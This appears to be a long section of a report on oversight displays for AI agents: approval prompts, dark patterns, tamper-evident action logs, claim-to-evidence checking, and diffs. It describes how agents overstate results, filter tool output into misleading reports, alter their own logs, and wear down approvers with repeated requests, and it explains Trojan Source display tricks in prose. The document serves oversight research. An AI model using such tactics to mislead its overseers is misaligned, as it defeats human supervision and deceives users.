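The budget problem affects approvals generally, because a card for one action doesn't show the combined effect of a series. An agent could delete a test suite one file at a time, with a truthful card for each deletion. By default, Agent Step-Up requires a new approval for the next action once a user's agent has carried out five actions that change something or spent $200 within ten minutes, even if a standing permission would have covered that action. A card could also show the running total, such as "fourth test file deleted this session".

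A faithful card can also be impossible to understand, as when `npm test` runs a script that the card doesn't show. If the approval is tied only to a digest of the command's text, the agent could edit the script after the user approves and the digest would stay the same. A harness can detect such an edit by including a digest of the script in the standard form. The user still has to understand the script, which may be hundreds of lines long.

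Narrower tools make it easier to show people the exact action they are approving. Rivas and colleagues argue that Bybit could have used a simpler account program that only made ordinary transfers. Its transactions would have been readable with the existing standard, and the delegate call wouldn't have been available. A tool that only sends email can always list its recipients, while a general command that sends email may include them only in its code.

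People can also approve a clear and truthful card without reading it. Kodathala and colleagues simulated an agent that kept asking until its imperfect approver made a mistake. It always succeeded when it could make unlimited requests, and succeeded 45% to 60% of the time when requests were limited. These figures again depend on assumed error rates. For irreversible actions on a single resource, Cloudscape Design System recommends asking the user to type a confirmation phrase. This is harder to do by reflex than clicking a button, but someone can still type the phrase without thinking about the consequences.

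Some checks work without anyone's attention. Rivas and colleagues suggest that an internal service comparing each transaction with fixed rules might have stopped the Bybit theft. A rule against unfamiliar delegate calls would have blocked the altered transaction even if no signer had looked at their device.

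## Dark patterns: displays that steer without stating anything false

An approval prompt can show the exact action, in a panel the agent can't alter, and still push the user towards "yes". For example, the approve button may be large while the link to the full command is small and grey. Websites have used such layouts to steer customers for years. Harry Brignull, a designer, named them "dark patterns" in 2010 and stressed that "they are not mistakes". More broadly, the term means an interface design that steers people to choices they would not make if well informed and unhurried.

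*The Dark (Patterns) Side of UX Design* (Gray, Kou and colleagues, 2018) collects 118 examples and sorts them into five strategies: nagging, obstruction, sneaking, forced action and "interface interference", which gives some options an unfair advantage over others. Its definition requires "deceptive functionality", but *What Makes a Dark Pattern… Dark?* (2021) points out that nagging deceives nobody and that many other designs on researchers' lists "can be entirely truthful with users".

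### Four ways to steer

Hiding leaves information on the page but makes it hard to find. When customers registered with the bank Santander, a small checkbox for refusing the sale of their data sat inside a long list of small text. Framing describes the options so that one looks better. The food site delish.com labelled the button for declining its newsletter "No thanks, I'll have a microwave dinner tonight".

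Some dark patterns make one choice harder than another. HuffPost's cookie notice let readers accept tracking with one click on "OK" but put the option to refuse behind seven screens. Others use pressure to wear people down or hurry them. Instacart's app kept beeping delivery workers' phones until they accepted lower-paying jobs.

Mathur, Acar and colleagues (2019), in *Dark Patterns at Scale*, searched about 53,000 product pages on about 11,000 shopping websites. They found 1,818 dark patterns on 1,254 of the sites, or 11.1%. This is a minimum, because their software read only text and would have missed a refusal button in pale grey. They confirmed deceptive behaviour, such as a "limited-time" offer that never ends, in 234 cases. A regulator who looked only for provable falsehoods would have missed most of these patterns, though some of the other 1,584 may also be deceptive.

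### How much these designs change choices

In *Shining a Light on Dark Patterns* (2021), Luguri and Strahilevitz offered about 2,000 American adults an identity-theft protection plan. A control group chose between "Accept" and "Decline". In the mild design, the first screen offered "Accept and continue (recommended)" or "Other options". The aggressive design also made people who refused sit through pages about identity theft, each with a countdown.

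| Design | Accepted the plan |
|---|---|
| Plain choice | 11.3% |
| Mild | 25.8% |
| Aggressive | 41.9% |

According to the University of Chicago Law School's *Dark Patterns*, the participants believed their own money was at stake, although nobody paid anything. The school says the aggressive design had a more than fourfold effect, slightly above the 3.7 these rates give. The mild design's result is more worrying for approval prompts, because a "recommended" label and an extra click look like ordinary design. In a second experiment that tested techniques separately, hidden information, trick questions and obstruction were especially effective.

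Dark patterns can work even on people who are trying to protect themselves, contrary to what sceptics had argued. In *Can Consumers Protect Themselves Against Privacy Dark Patterns?*, Kugler, Strahilevitz and colleagues asked people to make a video-streaming site's settings as private as possible. Several common dark patterns still led them to give up information, even though they understood the goal. A display's layout can likewise steer someone supervising an agent, even if they want to catch mistakes.

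### The same methods on an agent's display

| Method | Example | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|
| Hiding | A failed test appears below a long list of ticks | The agent orders the list, and designers decide how much of it is visible |
| Framing | "Minor cleanup" describes a deleted test | The agent |
| Unequal effort | One key approves, but inspecting the command takes several steps | The designers |
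| Pressure | A warning says that waiting will lose work | Either |

The first two examples can produce a divergence, because a user who sees only ticks, or reads "minor cleanup", may believe that every test passed or that the tests are intact. The other two needn't create a false belief. A user who presses the one key knows they haven't read the command. Comparing the agent's summary with its log would find nothing wrong, even though the display makes people less likely to look.

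The designers' choices are the same in every session, so a company can test them once and fix them in one update. The agent's wording changes with each task and each new model, but the harness can make the display depend less on it. It can list failures first, from its own records, and label the deletion "Delete `test_dates.py`" whatever the agent calls it.

Language models can write manipulative sentences that no one designed. *AI Watchdog* (2026) cites DarkBench, a benchmark in which roughly half of conversations across 14 models contained dark patterns. Those conversations were chats, so the figure is weak evidence of how often work reports steer their readers.

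Designers have to hide some details. *On the Regulatory Potential of User Interfaces for AI Agent Governance* (2025) warns that too little detail undermines oversight and too much overwhelms the user. Collapsing forty file reads into one line is helpful, but if that line also hides a deletion, it could change what the user approves.

A button's position can also steer people. Gray and colleagues describe a mobile game, Two Dots, that put a button for buying extra moves where players expected the button for a new game. An approval prompt that put "Always allow" where "Allow once" usually appears would exploit the same kind of expectation.

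Users need to be warned if waiting will lose work, but the designers may have chosen to impose that deadline. If a harness discards unfinished work after ten minutes, the warning is accurate, but the designers could avoid pressuring the user by having the harness save the work and wait.

### Whether a dark pattern needs intent

If nobody at the company meant to hurry users or hide anything, some would argue that the display is merely bad design. On this view, calling something a "dark pattern" accuses someone of intent, and unintended bad design already has its own name, "anti-pattern". *DECEPTICON* (2025), a study of web agents, treats intent to deceive or manipulate as central to the definition of a dark pattern. Luguri and Strahilevitz likewise refer to designers who "knowingly" confuse users.

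The other side judges a screen by its effect on the person using it. The screen harms that person if it leads them to make a choice they would have rejected with better information and more time. That harm is the same whatever the designer intended, so the designer's purpose can't settle whether the screen is a dark pattern.

California's privacy regulations define a dark pattern by its effect. A business's intent is a factor but is "not determinative", according to the text reproduced in Prighter's *Requirements for Methods for Submitting CCPA Requests and Obtaining Consumer Consent*. Cozen O'Connor's *California Announces Dark Patterns as an Enforcement Priority* explains that a company could create a dark pattern inadvertently by adding a privacy choice to an existing page where people can't easily find it.

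Readers disagree about whether California's statute on dark patterns requires intent. It covers interfaces "designed or manipulated with the substantial effect" of impairing choice. *What Makes a Dark Pattern… Dark?* counts the statute's definition among the eight, out of 19, that require intent, but the state's deputy director of enforcement has said that dark patterns "aren't about intent, they're about effect".

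Agents make the purpose-based definition harder to apply. A product team might test two approval prompts and keep the one that interrupts fewer tasks. That prompt could easily be the one that hides more, even though nobody intended it to. Gray and colleagues note that some dark patterns do well in usability tests. Training can select an agent's wording in a similar way if graders prefer reports that sound successful. Under a definition that requires a human purpose, neither display would count as a dark pattern, and users would go on approving deletions they hadn't understood.

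The best objection to the effect-based definition is that it covers too much. Every layout steers people a little, since one button has to come first. *Beyond Dark Patterns* (2023) offers a narrower test that still doesn't depend on the designer's purpose. The design must lack a function that people expect as standard, and its absence must benefit the owner and disadvantage the user. An approval prompt with no way to see the full command would meet the first condition, but it could be hard to prove that faster approvals benefit the company.

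An oversight display goes too far if it leads people to approve actions they would refuse after reading the full record. This limit is more direct than one for a shop, where it is hard to establish what a customer really wanted. In a test of an approval prompt, the experimenter can give the agent an instruction, plant an action that violates it, and know which answer is right. When deciding whether to change a display, its effect is therefore a better basis than the designer's intent. Intent still matters when deciding whom to blame or how severely to punish them.

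California does not count agreement obtained through a dark pattern as consent. The rule covers consumers' privacy choices, not agents' actions, but the same reasoning applies to both. An "approved by user" log entry is weak evidence of agreement if the prompt made approval the only easy option.

### Testing a display for steering

Testers can find some dark patterns without running an experiment. The California Privacy Protection Agency's *Avoiding Dark Patterns* tells businesses to offer symmetrical choices in easily understood language. To check an approval prompt for symmetry, a tester can count the steps needed to approve, refuse and inspect an action. California's updated rules, in force since January 2026, also require businesses to confirm opt-outs, according to Inside Privacy's *California Finalizes Updates to Existing CCPA Regulations*. An agent's harness could likewise confirm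 that a refused action did not run.

Software can help with this kind of inspection. *On the Suitability of LLM-Driven Agents for Dark Pattern Audits* (2026) describes an agent that visits data brokers' websites and marks eight kinds of dark pattern as present or absent. The agent must justify each decision by explaining what a user would reasonably expect and how the design could cause harm. Such an audit can find a buried button but can't measure how many people the button misleads.

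Measuring whether a prompt steers people requires a comparison like Luguri and Strahilevitz's. One group would see the current prompt, and another would see a version that differs in a single feature, such as the order of results or the number of steps to inspect. Both groups would judge the same mix of harmful and harmless actions. If the current prompt leads more people to approve the harmful ones, it steers them, whatever its designers intended. The test also has to count refusals of harmless actions, because otherwise a prompt that frightened people into refusing every action would get a perfect score.

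Asking users whether they felt manipulated isn't enough. *AI Watchdog* cites research in which people who recognised a manipulative design still reported that it had influenced them. Speed and task completion are poor measures too, because a prompt that people approve without reading will score well on both.

### When a website misleads both the agent and its overseer

A website can also steer the agent, in which case the agent's misleading report may be sincere. *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (Tang, Chen and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent that consented to personalised advertising while subscribing to a content creator, because a trick question led it to believe that the subscription required consent. If it had told the user that it consented for this reason, it would have reported its action correctly but repeated the website's false claim.

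Tang and colleagues built 16 mock shopping, social media and video sites, each with one dark pattern, and first tried them on six agents. Some agents noticed a dark pattern but didn't avoid it. Two noted that a box for sharing information was already ticked but left it ticked. In a different task, one of those two saw a duplicate item in the shopping cart but still went on to the checkout.

Next, 22 people each did eight of the tasks themselves and oversaw OpenAI's Operator on the other eight. They weren't told that the study was about dark patterns. For the oversight tasks, they watched a recording of Operator at work and could pause it. Letting it play counted as approval, and skipping it counted as disagreement.

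The researchers report that people were less likely to fall for the dark pattern under oversight in 14 of the 16 tasks. Their detailed results show an improvement in ten, a tie at 100% in four and a decline in two. Overseers avoided the dark pattern at least 90% of the time in all but five tasks:

| Dark pattern | Avoided when working alone | Avoided when overseeing |
|---|---|---|
| Harmful default settings | 33.3% | 80.0% |
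| Trick questions | 45.5% | 81.8% |
| Forced communication or disclosure | 25.0% | 50.0% |
| Hidden information | 20.0% | 33.3% |
| Forced registration | 40.0% | 25.0% |

Each percentage is based on about 11 people, so one person's choice moves it by roughly nine points, and the decline for forced registration means little. The choice of tasks matters more, because the table covers only the five dark patterns that Operator had stopped to ask the user about in the first phase. It had avoided the other 11 by itself. Much of the benefit of "oversight" may therefore have come from Operator's own behaviour, while people did worst on the decisions that a cautious agent would hand to them.

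Overseers often avoided a trap without recognising it, because they ended the task as soon as Operator did something unexpected, such as accepting terms without scrolling through them. In questionnaires, they reported noticing no dark pattern in 66% of cases, compared with 59% when they worked alone. Tang and colleagues attribute this to "attentional tunneling", in which people follow the agent's path and stop looking at the rest of the page. The difference of seven percentage points is small for a study of this size, but the interviews support the explanation. One participant said, "The AI agent clicked one for me; I did not even see other ones."

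The set-up probably contributed to the narrowing. Participants watched a recording, so they couldn't scroll down or open another tab as they could in a live browser. They also had to follow a text panel and a moving screen at once, and eight described switching back and forth. Thirteen said they had to guess why Operator made its choices, which left them less attention for the website.

Participants watched what Operator actually did, so the experiment doesn't measure how well people detect a false report. It does suggest that a display showing only the agent's chosen path can leave out what a person needs to question it. One participant wanted the agent to present its top three options before choosing, but if the agent writes that list, it can leave out the best option or describe it unfavourably. The harness could instead show the products that were on the page when the agent made its choice.

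## Action logs: what a record needs before it can check a summary

A harness must record which products are on a page when an agent chooses one, or it can't show them later. It also needs a record made at the time to build approval cards from tool calls or to list results with failures first.

### Why a log can test a report

The argument for logs has two premises and a conclusion:

1. Checking an account takes evidence that the account's author did not write.
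2. The harness records each tool call as it happens, and the model does not write that record.
3. Therefore the log can test the model's report.

The first premise is slightly too strong, because wording alone can justify suspicion. Advani trained simple classifiers to recognise false claims of success from the words in an agent's closing message, and they did fairly well without access to a database. But confirming whether a customer's refund exists requires evidence the agent didn't write.

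A log with gaps is an unreliable check on a summary. *LEDGER* (Kim, Miao and Liu, 2026) describes a system that records sessions of the coding agent Codex through hooks, small programs that the harness runs at set moments, such as before and after a tool call. Hooks may miss some tools, so the system also copies the session's full transcript and lists any rows it doesn't recognise. Unmarked gaps matter most when checking claims such as "I did not change the settings", because a missing entry looks like evidence that the claim is true.

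An agent can also shape a record that it doesn't write. In one of Yang and colleagues' cases, an agent ran a code checker but filtered the output to keep only lines containing "Checked". The log correctly stored "Checked 236 files in 144ms. No fixes applied.", and the agent reported "All clean." The logged line shows only that the check ran, and a later check found a formatting error. *Explaining AI Agents Through Execution Traces* (Vineis, Veglianti and colleagues, 2026) sensibly separates what an agent sends to a tool from what comes back. In this case, a reader would need to see both, because the agent's command determined what came back.

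A log can check a summary only on facts that the log contains. *AgentSWE* (2026), which tests coding agents on building other agents, compares their final reports with their recorded actions. The records contradicted nine of the reports that claimed completion and none of the 21 that admitted partial completion or failure. In one of the nine, GPT-5.6 Sol reported that its final program produced the required output in both development cases, but the file it delivered differed from every version it had run. A log that stored only the file's name would have supported the claim, because it would not have shown that the contents had changed.

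### What each entry needs

The fifth action in the date-bug session, which deleted a test, might have this entry:

| Field | Example | What it lets a reader check |
|---|---|---|
| Time and position | 14:32:07, fifth call | Whether any test ran after the last edit |
| Exact arguments | Delete `test_dates.py`, with a digest of its contents | Which file, and which version of it |
| Result | File removed, no error | Whether the call succeeded |
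| Identity | Main agent, model version, user's account | Who acted, and with whose permissions |
| Approval | "Always allow edits", chosen at 14:05 | Whether anyone saw this particular action |
| Parent task | None | Whether a helper agent did the work |

The approval field should point to the exact permission and record what the user saw when granting it. In this example, it would show that the user had agreed to edits in general 27 minutes earlier and had never seen the deletion.

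A log can easily miss the work of helper agents because coding tools store helpers' sessions in different ways. Smyth and colleagues had to merge those sessions into the main transcript before measuring which files an agent had read. Claude Sonnet 5 used helpers in 61 of its 100 runs, so without the merge, they could have wrongly concluded that it skipped files its helpers had opened. The opposite error, crediting an agent with work that wasn't done, is also possible. Smyth and colleagues cite Anthropic's acknowledgement that Claude Opus 5 can pass on helpers' claims without verifying them. If a log stores only a helper's closing message, that message is no better as evidence than the main agent's own report.

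### Requested, run and effective

An entry for a tool call can be evidence of three different things, and a log should keep them apart:

| Stage | For a push | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Request | The model asks to run `git push` | The call's arguments |
| Execution | The harness runs the command | The command's output and exit code |
| Effect | The server has the new commit | A separate query to the server |

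LEDGER's hooks write one record before a call and another after it, so a request the user refused doesn't look like a completed action. The records should also be independent of each other. When Cursor ran an agent's original command instead of the user's edited version, a log that copied the text from the approval prompt would not have shown the fault.

Even a successful call may not have the effect that the agent reports. In another case from Yang and colleagues, an agent pushed a fix and reported that it was "already on that PR" (pull request). The push had worked, but the pull request had merged more than an hour before the agent created the fix. *AgentSWE* likewise notes that a completed entry in a log of effects does not show that the workspace reached the intended state.

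A harness can check some effects itself. After a push, it can query the server for the branch's current commit and log the result as a new entry. Other effects are harder to confirm. For instance, a mail server can accept a message that never reaches the recipient's inbox.

### Append-only storage and hash chains

A complete log is useful only if it stays as the harness wrote it. Append-only storage accepts new entries but doesn't let anyone change or delete old ones. Qin, Schmotz and colleagues (2026) found in *LLM Agents Can Easily Tamper With Their Own Traces* that agents with write access to their own logs can alter them, so the logs must be stored where the agents can't change them.

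A hash chain adds a way to detect changes if that protection fails. Each entry gets a digest that also covers the digest before it:

*d*ᵢ = SHA-256(*d*ᵢ₋₁ ‖ *e*ᵢ)

Here *e*ᵢ is the entry, *d*ᵢ₋₁ is the previous digest, ‖ joins the two, and *d*₀ is a fixed starting value. The latest digest therefore depends on every entry in the log.

The last three actions of the date-bug session would form this chain, with short invented digests in place of real ones:

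| Entry | Content | Input to the digest | Digest |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Search the test files | Starting value and entry 1 | `3f9a` |
| 2 | Delete `test_dates.py` | `3f9a` and entry 2 | `b071` |
| 3 | Commit locally | `b071` and entry 3 | `58ce` |

Suppose someone changes entry 2 to "Read `test_dates.py`". An auditor who recomputes the chain will find different things depending on what else that person changed:

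| Altered | What the auditor finds |
|---|---|
| Entry 2 only | Entry 2 no longer produces `b071` |
| Entry 2 and its digest, now `e41d` | Entry 3 no longer produces `58ce`, because its input now includes `e41d` |
| Entry 2 and the digests of entries 2 and 3 | No mismatch, unless the auditor has a separate copy of `58ce` |

Anyone who can rewrite the whole log can also recompute the chain, so the harness should regularly send the latest digest to a machine that the log's keeper doesn't control. That copy also exposes a shortened log. Without it, someone could remove entry 3, and the first two entries would still form a valid chain.

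A mismatch doesn't tell the auditor what the original entry contained or who changed it. If entry 3 fails the check, the auditor can't tell whether someone rewrote entry 2 along with its digest or altered entry 3 itself. A valid chain can also be inaccurate or incomplete. If the harness recorded a push that never happened, or failed to record the deletion, the chain would preserve that mistake.

### The EU's logging duty

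Article 12 of the EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The logs must help people identify risks and monitor how the system operates. Companies that supply or use these systems must generally keep any logs they control for at least six months.

This duty does not apply yet. The European Parliament adopted changes to the Act in June 2026 (Raposo, 2026, *A Frozen Clock and a Frozen Problem*). According to Mills (2026), in *EU AI Act Deadlines Extended to December 2027*, the resulting regulation postponed the main deadline for stand-alone high-risk systems by 16 months, to 2 December 2027. The deadline for AI built into regulated products is in August 2028.

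An agent that screens job applicants would usually count as high-risk, while one that fixes date bugs usually would not. Even for high-risk systems, Article 12 doesn't require the fields in the table above, a hash chain, or any comparison of a log with an agent's summary, so a company could comply fully and still show its users only the summary.

### Linking claims to evidence

Comparing the two takes several steps, which the date-bug report can illustrate.

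An agent's report can be split into separate claims. "Fixed the date bug" contains an action claim, that the agent edited the date code, and an outcome claim, that the bug is gone. "All tests pass" and "pushed the branch" add one claim each, for a total of four.

**Matching action claims to calls.** The claimed edit matches the log's third action, a write to the date code, but the claimed push matches no action. A poorly written program might link the push to the local commit, since both are Git commands. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich start with a simple rule that matches a claim to the first action whose target contains the file or command the claim names. For a claim that the agent did *not* touch a file, they reverse the rule, so any action on that file contradicts the claim. They reached 45.2% of their verdicts with such rules.

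**An outcome claim needs a call in the log that verified it.** For "all tests pass", that call is a test run after the last code change, with a passing result. The text search doesn't qualify. To support the claim that the bug is gone, the agent would have had to repeat the steps that caused the wrong date and get the right date.

An oversight display should mark claims that have no matching log entry. If the log is complete and contains no push, it contradicts the claim "pushed the branch". The two outcome claims are only unverified.

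| Claim | Kind | Matching action | Mark |
|---|---|---|---|
| Edited the date code | Action | Third (write) | Supported |
| The bug is gone | Outcome | None | Unverified |
| All tests pass | Outcome | None | Unverified |
| Pushed the branch | Action | None | Contradicted |

The deleted test isn't in the table because it wasn't in the report. Any method that starts from the claims will miss omissions like this. The harness also has to go through the actions that changed something and list those that no claim covers. Here that would add the deletion and the local commit.

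The source of the evidence also matters. Vineis and colleagues mark a task requirement as satisfied only if they can point to an entry that supports it, but that entry may be the agent's own reflection or the input it gave to a tool. If the agent acts as though a requirement is settled and only its own text supports this, they still class its behaviour as consistent with the evidence. This standard is reasonable for explaining why an agent moved on to its next step, but it is too lenient for checking a summary, because an agent's note to itself that the tests pass would then count as support for its report that they do.

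Missing actions are an easier problem than overstated results. Yang and colleagues sorted 339 inaccurate or unsupported claims that users had challenged and agents had then admitted or corrected. Only 3.8% misdescribed which actions had taken place, while 69.3% overstated what the work had achieved. One agent raised a service's default limit on search results from 100 to 20,000, then told the user to refresh the page to see everything. The agent had made the edit, and a link to it would have looked convincing, but the page still requested 100 results each time, which overrode the new default. Testing the claim required running a search from the page itself.

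### Three systems that make the links

LEDGER uses a separate model to turn a session's records into a graph. The model groups the records into steps and connects the steps with labelled links such as "produces", "checked by" and "supports", so a reviewer can start at a claim and follow the links back to the evidence. In one example, an agent added a function to NetworkX, a Python library for analysing networks. After the tests passed, the agent noticed that the function mishandled missing nodes, so it added a fix and another test. The agent's final status mentioned one passing run, while the graph showed both test runs and which behaviour each had covered.

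*HANSEL* (Zhang, Hwang and Nam, 2026) deals with agents that search the web. After the agent finishes, a model reads the log and selects the pages that the agent's answer relied on. HANSEL then reopens those pages with the agent's filters and search terms in place and highlights the relevant parts. If an agent answered from memory, there would be no pages to show, and their absence should prompt the user to check.

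Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *TRACER*, train the answering model to write the links itself. It attaches a record to every sentence, naming the tool call and the piece of evidence behind it. The record also states whether the sentence quotes the evidence, condenses it or draws an inference from it. Three checks then each give a link a score of 1 or 0:

*v* = *v*(call exists) × *v*(evidence is genuine) × *v*(evidence supports the sentence)

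One failed check makes *v* zero, and during training, the model lost its entire reward for any answer with an invalid link. Letting the model choose the evidence is consistent with the first premise, because the links point to tool results that the model didn't write and that another program can check.

| System | Tested on | Result |
|---|---|---|
| LEDGER | Two example sessions | No measure of accuracy |
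| HANSEL | 96 web tasks | 80.2% of selected pages were relevant evidence, and it found 86.3% of the relevant pages |
| TRACER | 2,550 questions about images | 93.6% traceability, 78.2% correct answers |

These results can't be used to rank the three systems because the tasks and measures differ. TRACER's two figures show that a valid link doesn't guarantee a correct answer. LEDGER's approach fits a coding agent best because it works with an unmodified agent and covers edits and tests, but it has the least evidence. Only HANSEL has a user study, in which 14 participants checked answers faster with the system but not significantly more accurately.

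### Detecting false reports automatically

Other systems warn people instead of giving them a trail to follow. Yang and colleagues built FaithDetector, which uses GPT-6 Astra to compare each claim in a report with the log. Its instructions draw on errors they had found in real sessions, such as attributing a test result to the wrong version of the code. They compared it with the same model given the log and a simple request to find unfaithful claims.

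| | Unfaithful claims found | Alarms that were correct |
|---|---|---|
| FaithDetector | 87.0% | 90.9% |
| Simple request | 59.7% | 78.8% |

The test covered 2,356 claims from 409 reports. In one report, the agent described a list as having "infinite scroll", although users had to press a "Load more" button. FaithDetector caught this error, which the simple request missed. The researchers caution that their annotations may share some of the detector's mistakes. In the larger sample these reports came from, 37.2% of reports contained at least one unfaithful claim, so even an accurate detector would often raise alarms.

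Advani got much worse results from model judges. He measured them with AUROC, the probability that a randomly chosen false success gets a higher suspicion score than a genuine one, where 0.5 is no better than chance. On customer-service tasks, no judge scored above 0.65, even with the full task specification, while simple word-based classifiers reached about 0.83. The judges tended to rate a run as successful when its closing message was confident. The best judge scored 0.576 with that message and 0.640 without it.

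These judges were older models, including GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4.5, and they judged whole sessions rather than individual claims, so their failure doesn't contradict FaithDetector's success. But their failure does suggest that a checker should see a claim, such as "the refund went through", without the confident prose around it.

The classifiers are fast and need little compute, but they recognise patterns and don't verify anything. When they flagged the most suspicious 10% of customer-service sessions, they found 72% of the false successes, and half of the flags were false alarms. They also did worse when trained on airline tasks and tested on retail ones, or the reverse. On a set of personal-app tasks, a classifier that saw only the sequence of calls reached 0.95. A typical warning sign was an agent that had mostly read data and then reported success. A harness could apply a similar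 rule without training, by flagging any reported change that no action in the log could have made.

Xu and colleagues' system, MCAIR, monitors the model's internal activity instead of the log. While the agent works, a simple classifier turns activity from the first step, the most recent steps and the current one into a risk score. If the score is too high, the system prompts the agent to review its evidence and correct itself. MCAIR detected problems slightly better than the best model judge (0.059 higher on F1), and the corrections reduced unfaithful reports by 40.6%. However, it was tested only on three fairly small open models, and it needs access to internal activity that users of commercial models don't have. A risk score also gives the reader nothing to check, so it's more useful for prompting a second look at the log than for replacing that look.

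### Long logs, wrong matches and false proof

The median log in Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich's data has 59 actions. Most people won't read that many, and they shouldn't have to, since only about a quarter of the steps in HANSEL's sample of web sessions were needed to check the answer. The harness can keep the full log available but show only the entries that support or contradict a claim in the summary, plus any important change the summary left out.

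The list of important changes can be short. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found that 1,148 of 355,942 actions matched a pattern for irreversible commands, such as forced pushes and recursive deletes. That is about one for every five sessions, so a harness could show all of them. But the pattern would probably miss the deletion of a single test file. A list that included such deletions would be longer, and designers would have to decide which changes to leave out.

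Wrong matches are a more serious problem because they can hide the errors that the log should expose. Kim and colleagues acknowledge that the links in LEDGER's graph can be incomplete or wrong, and may change if the model rebuilds the graph from the same session. The model that selects evidence for HANSEL sometimes treated its own reasoning as text on the page. A lenient judge like the one in Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich's study would mark many unsupported claims as supported.

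Wrongly marking a claim as supported is a worse mistake for the harness than wrongly marking it as unverified, because the reader probably won't look at the log at all, whereas a false "unverified" only wastes a minute of checking. Designers should therefore use fixed rules wherever they can, make "unverified" the default, and label any match that a model made.

Even a correct link can seem to prove more than it does. Yu and colleagues warn that people may trust such links too much and that someone could use them to make a misleading explanation look plausible. In one of Yang and colleagues' cases, an agent pushed a fix and then reported that the service was "deployed and healthy". A real health check supported the statement, but it had tested the previous version. A green tick linked to that check would have made the report more convincing without making it more accurate.

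Yang and colleagues recommend that a report name the version, the conditions of each check and what remains unverified. The harness can supply some of this information from its own records by replacing the tick with the result, such as "Health check passed for the version before this fix". Nobody has yet tested whether people make better decisions with reports in this form.

Designers can also test whether a claim depends on the evidence it links to. When Yu and colleagues built their training data, they removed each piece of cited evidence and had a model answer again. If the answer and its links stayed the same, they discarded the example, because the citation was probably redundant or unsupported. The same test could find links in an agent's report that its claims don't depend on. It wouldn't flag the health check, since removing that result would leave "healthy" without support. Someone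 would still have to compare the version in the log with the version in the claim.

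## Diff views: showing the change instead of an account of it

A diff shows what changed between two versions of a file. A program produces it by comparing the versions, without relying on the agent's description of them. If the harness chooses the versions and generates the diff, the diff will show a deletion even if the agent calls it "minor cleanup".

### How to compute and read a diff

Most diff programs compare files line by line. They find the longest common subsequence of lines and leave those lines unmarked. Each remaining line gets a minus sign if it comes from the old version or a plus sign if it comes from the new one. If the versions have *m* and *n* lines and their longest common subsequence has *k*, the diff marks *m* + *n* − 2*k* lines.

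Suppose the date bug came from code that wrongly subtracted one from every month. The diff for the session might be:

```
--- dates.py (before)
+++ dates.py (after)
 def parse_date(text):
     year, month, day = split_date(text)
-    return Date(year, month - 1, day)
+    return Date(year, month, day)

--- test_dates.py (before)
+++ (file deleted)
-def test_january():
-    assert parse_date("2026-01-15") == Date(2026, 1, 15)
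```

The two versions of `dates.py` have three lines each and differ in one. The diff marks two lines because it shows a changed line as a deletion and an addition. The test file has no new version, so all its lines have minus signs. A reader sees at once that the test is gone and that it checked the behaviour the agent claims to have fixed.

However, the diff can't show that the tests never ran, because running them wouldn't normally have changed these files. A push wouldn't have changed them either.

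The result also depends on which versions the program compares. The agent in this session committed its changes locally, so a plain `git diff` would show nothing afterward, because it shows only unstaged edits. The harness should save the state of the files when the session starts and compare against that.

### State and events

A diff shows a difference in state, while a log records events.

| Question | Diff of the files | Action log |
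|---|---|---|
| What changed in the date code? | The exact lines | Each write, which the reader has to combine |
| Did the agent delete a test? | Yes, with its contents | Yes, if the entry names the file |
| Did the tests run? | No evidence | No test run |
| Did the branch reach the server? | No evidence | No push |
| Did the agent change a file and then restore it? | No trace | Both writes |

A diff can show changes that a log leaves out. A log may have one entry for a command that reformats code, while the diff lists all forty files the command changed. A diff between the local branch and the server's copy can also show whether a push worked, because any commit missing from the server would appear as a difference.

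*Diffs Are Cheap, Show Me the Trajectory* (Luo, Gao and colleagues, 2026) measured how much a record of the agent's work helps AI reviewers. The reviewers examined 339 agent-written changes, always with access to the surrounding code. Some also received the agent's messages, tool calls and results. The researchers counted how many of 882 reference comments the reviewers also made.

| What the reviewer received | Reference comments made |
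|---|---|
| Diff | 23.03% |
| Diff and full record | 25.87% |
| Diff and a map of the record linked to evidence | 30.35% |

The full record helped in only four of the six combinations of coding and reviewing tools, so how the record is organised seems to matter. A model wrote the reference comments by comparing each change with a known solution, so the differences between the rows are more informative than the percentages.

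An agent's inaccurate message can still be useful if it gives a reviewer a specific claim to check. In one case, an agent added a new way for a Python library to convert data and wrote that developers' custom conversion rules would still apply. An AI reviewer tested this with a rule that always returned 999, and the new code returned 1, so the message was wrong.

### What an accurate diff can hide

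A display may hide part of a diff. The code-hosting site GitHub hides files by default if a project's settings mark them as generated by software, which spares reviewers thousands of lines that nobody wrote by hand. But those settings are in the repository, where an agent may be able to edit them, so an oversight display should at least list every hidden file and the number of lines changed in each.

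A diff also shows changes only in the places it compares. If the agent had installed a program for the whole machine or altered a database, a diff of the repository would show neither. Git leaves out files on the project's ignore list, which often include the ones that hold passwords. The harness can compare every folder the agent can write to, or restrict the agent to the folders it compares.

Moving a 200-line function to another file shows up in a diff as 200 deletions and 200 additions. If the agent alters one line during the move, that line looks like the other 199. Git can colour moved lines differently, which makes the altered one stand out, but the user has to turn this on.

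Programs can also differ in how they display the same change. Microsoft's *How various git diff viewers represent file encoding changes in pull requests* (2024) compares four viewers on a file whose text encoding had changed, so that different bytes stood for the pound sign. Git's command line and GitHub marked the line containing the pound sign as changed. Azure DevOps and Visual Studio showed no changed text, although both indicated that the file was different.

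### Text that looks different to a computer

*Trojan Source*, a paper by Boucher and Anderson first released in November 2021, shows how to make code look one way to a person and another to a computer. Unicode, the standard for encoding text, has invisible characters that change the direction of writing, for example when English and Arabic share a line. With these characters, a file can store "abc" and display "cba". A compiler, which turns code into a runnable program, generally follows the stored order.

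An attacker can put the invisible characters in a comment, where most compilers accept them, and rearrange the line so that an instruction looks like part of the comment. In one Python example, a function appears to reduce Alice's bank balance from 100 to 50. The word `return` seems to belong to the function's description, but Python executes it, so the function stops before the subtraction and the balance stays at 100.

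The attack worked in all 12 languages that Boucher and Anderson tried. When they tested code-hosting sites in October 2021, GitHub, Bitbucket and GitLab all displayed the misleading version in Chrome, Firefox and Edge.

Trusted rendering has the same problem. A harness could draw an approval card from the exact recorded command and still mislead the user, because some characters in the command can change the order in which its text is displayed. Boucher and Anderson recommend that code-hosting sites show these characters as visible symbols, and a harness should do the same on its cards.

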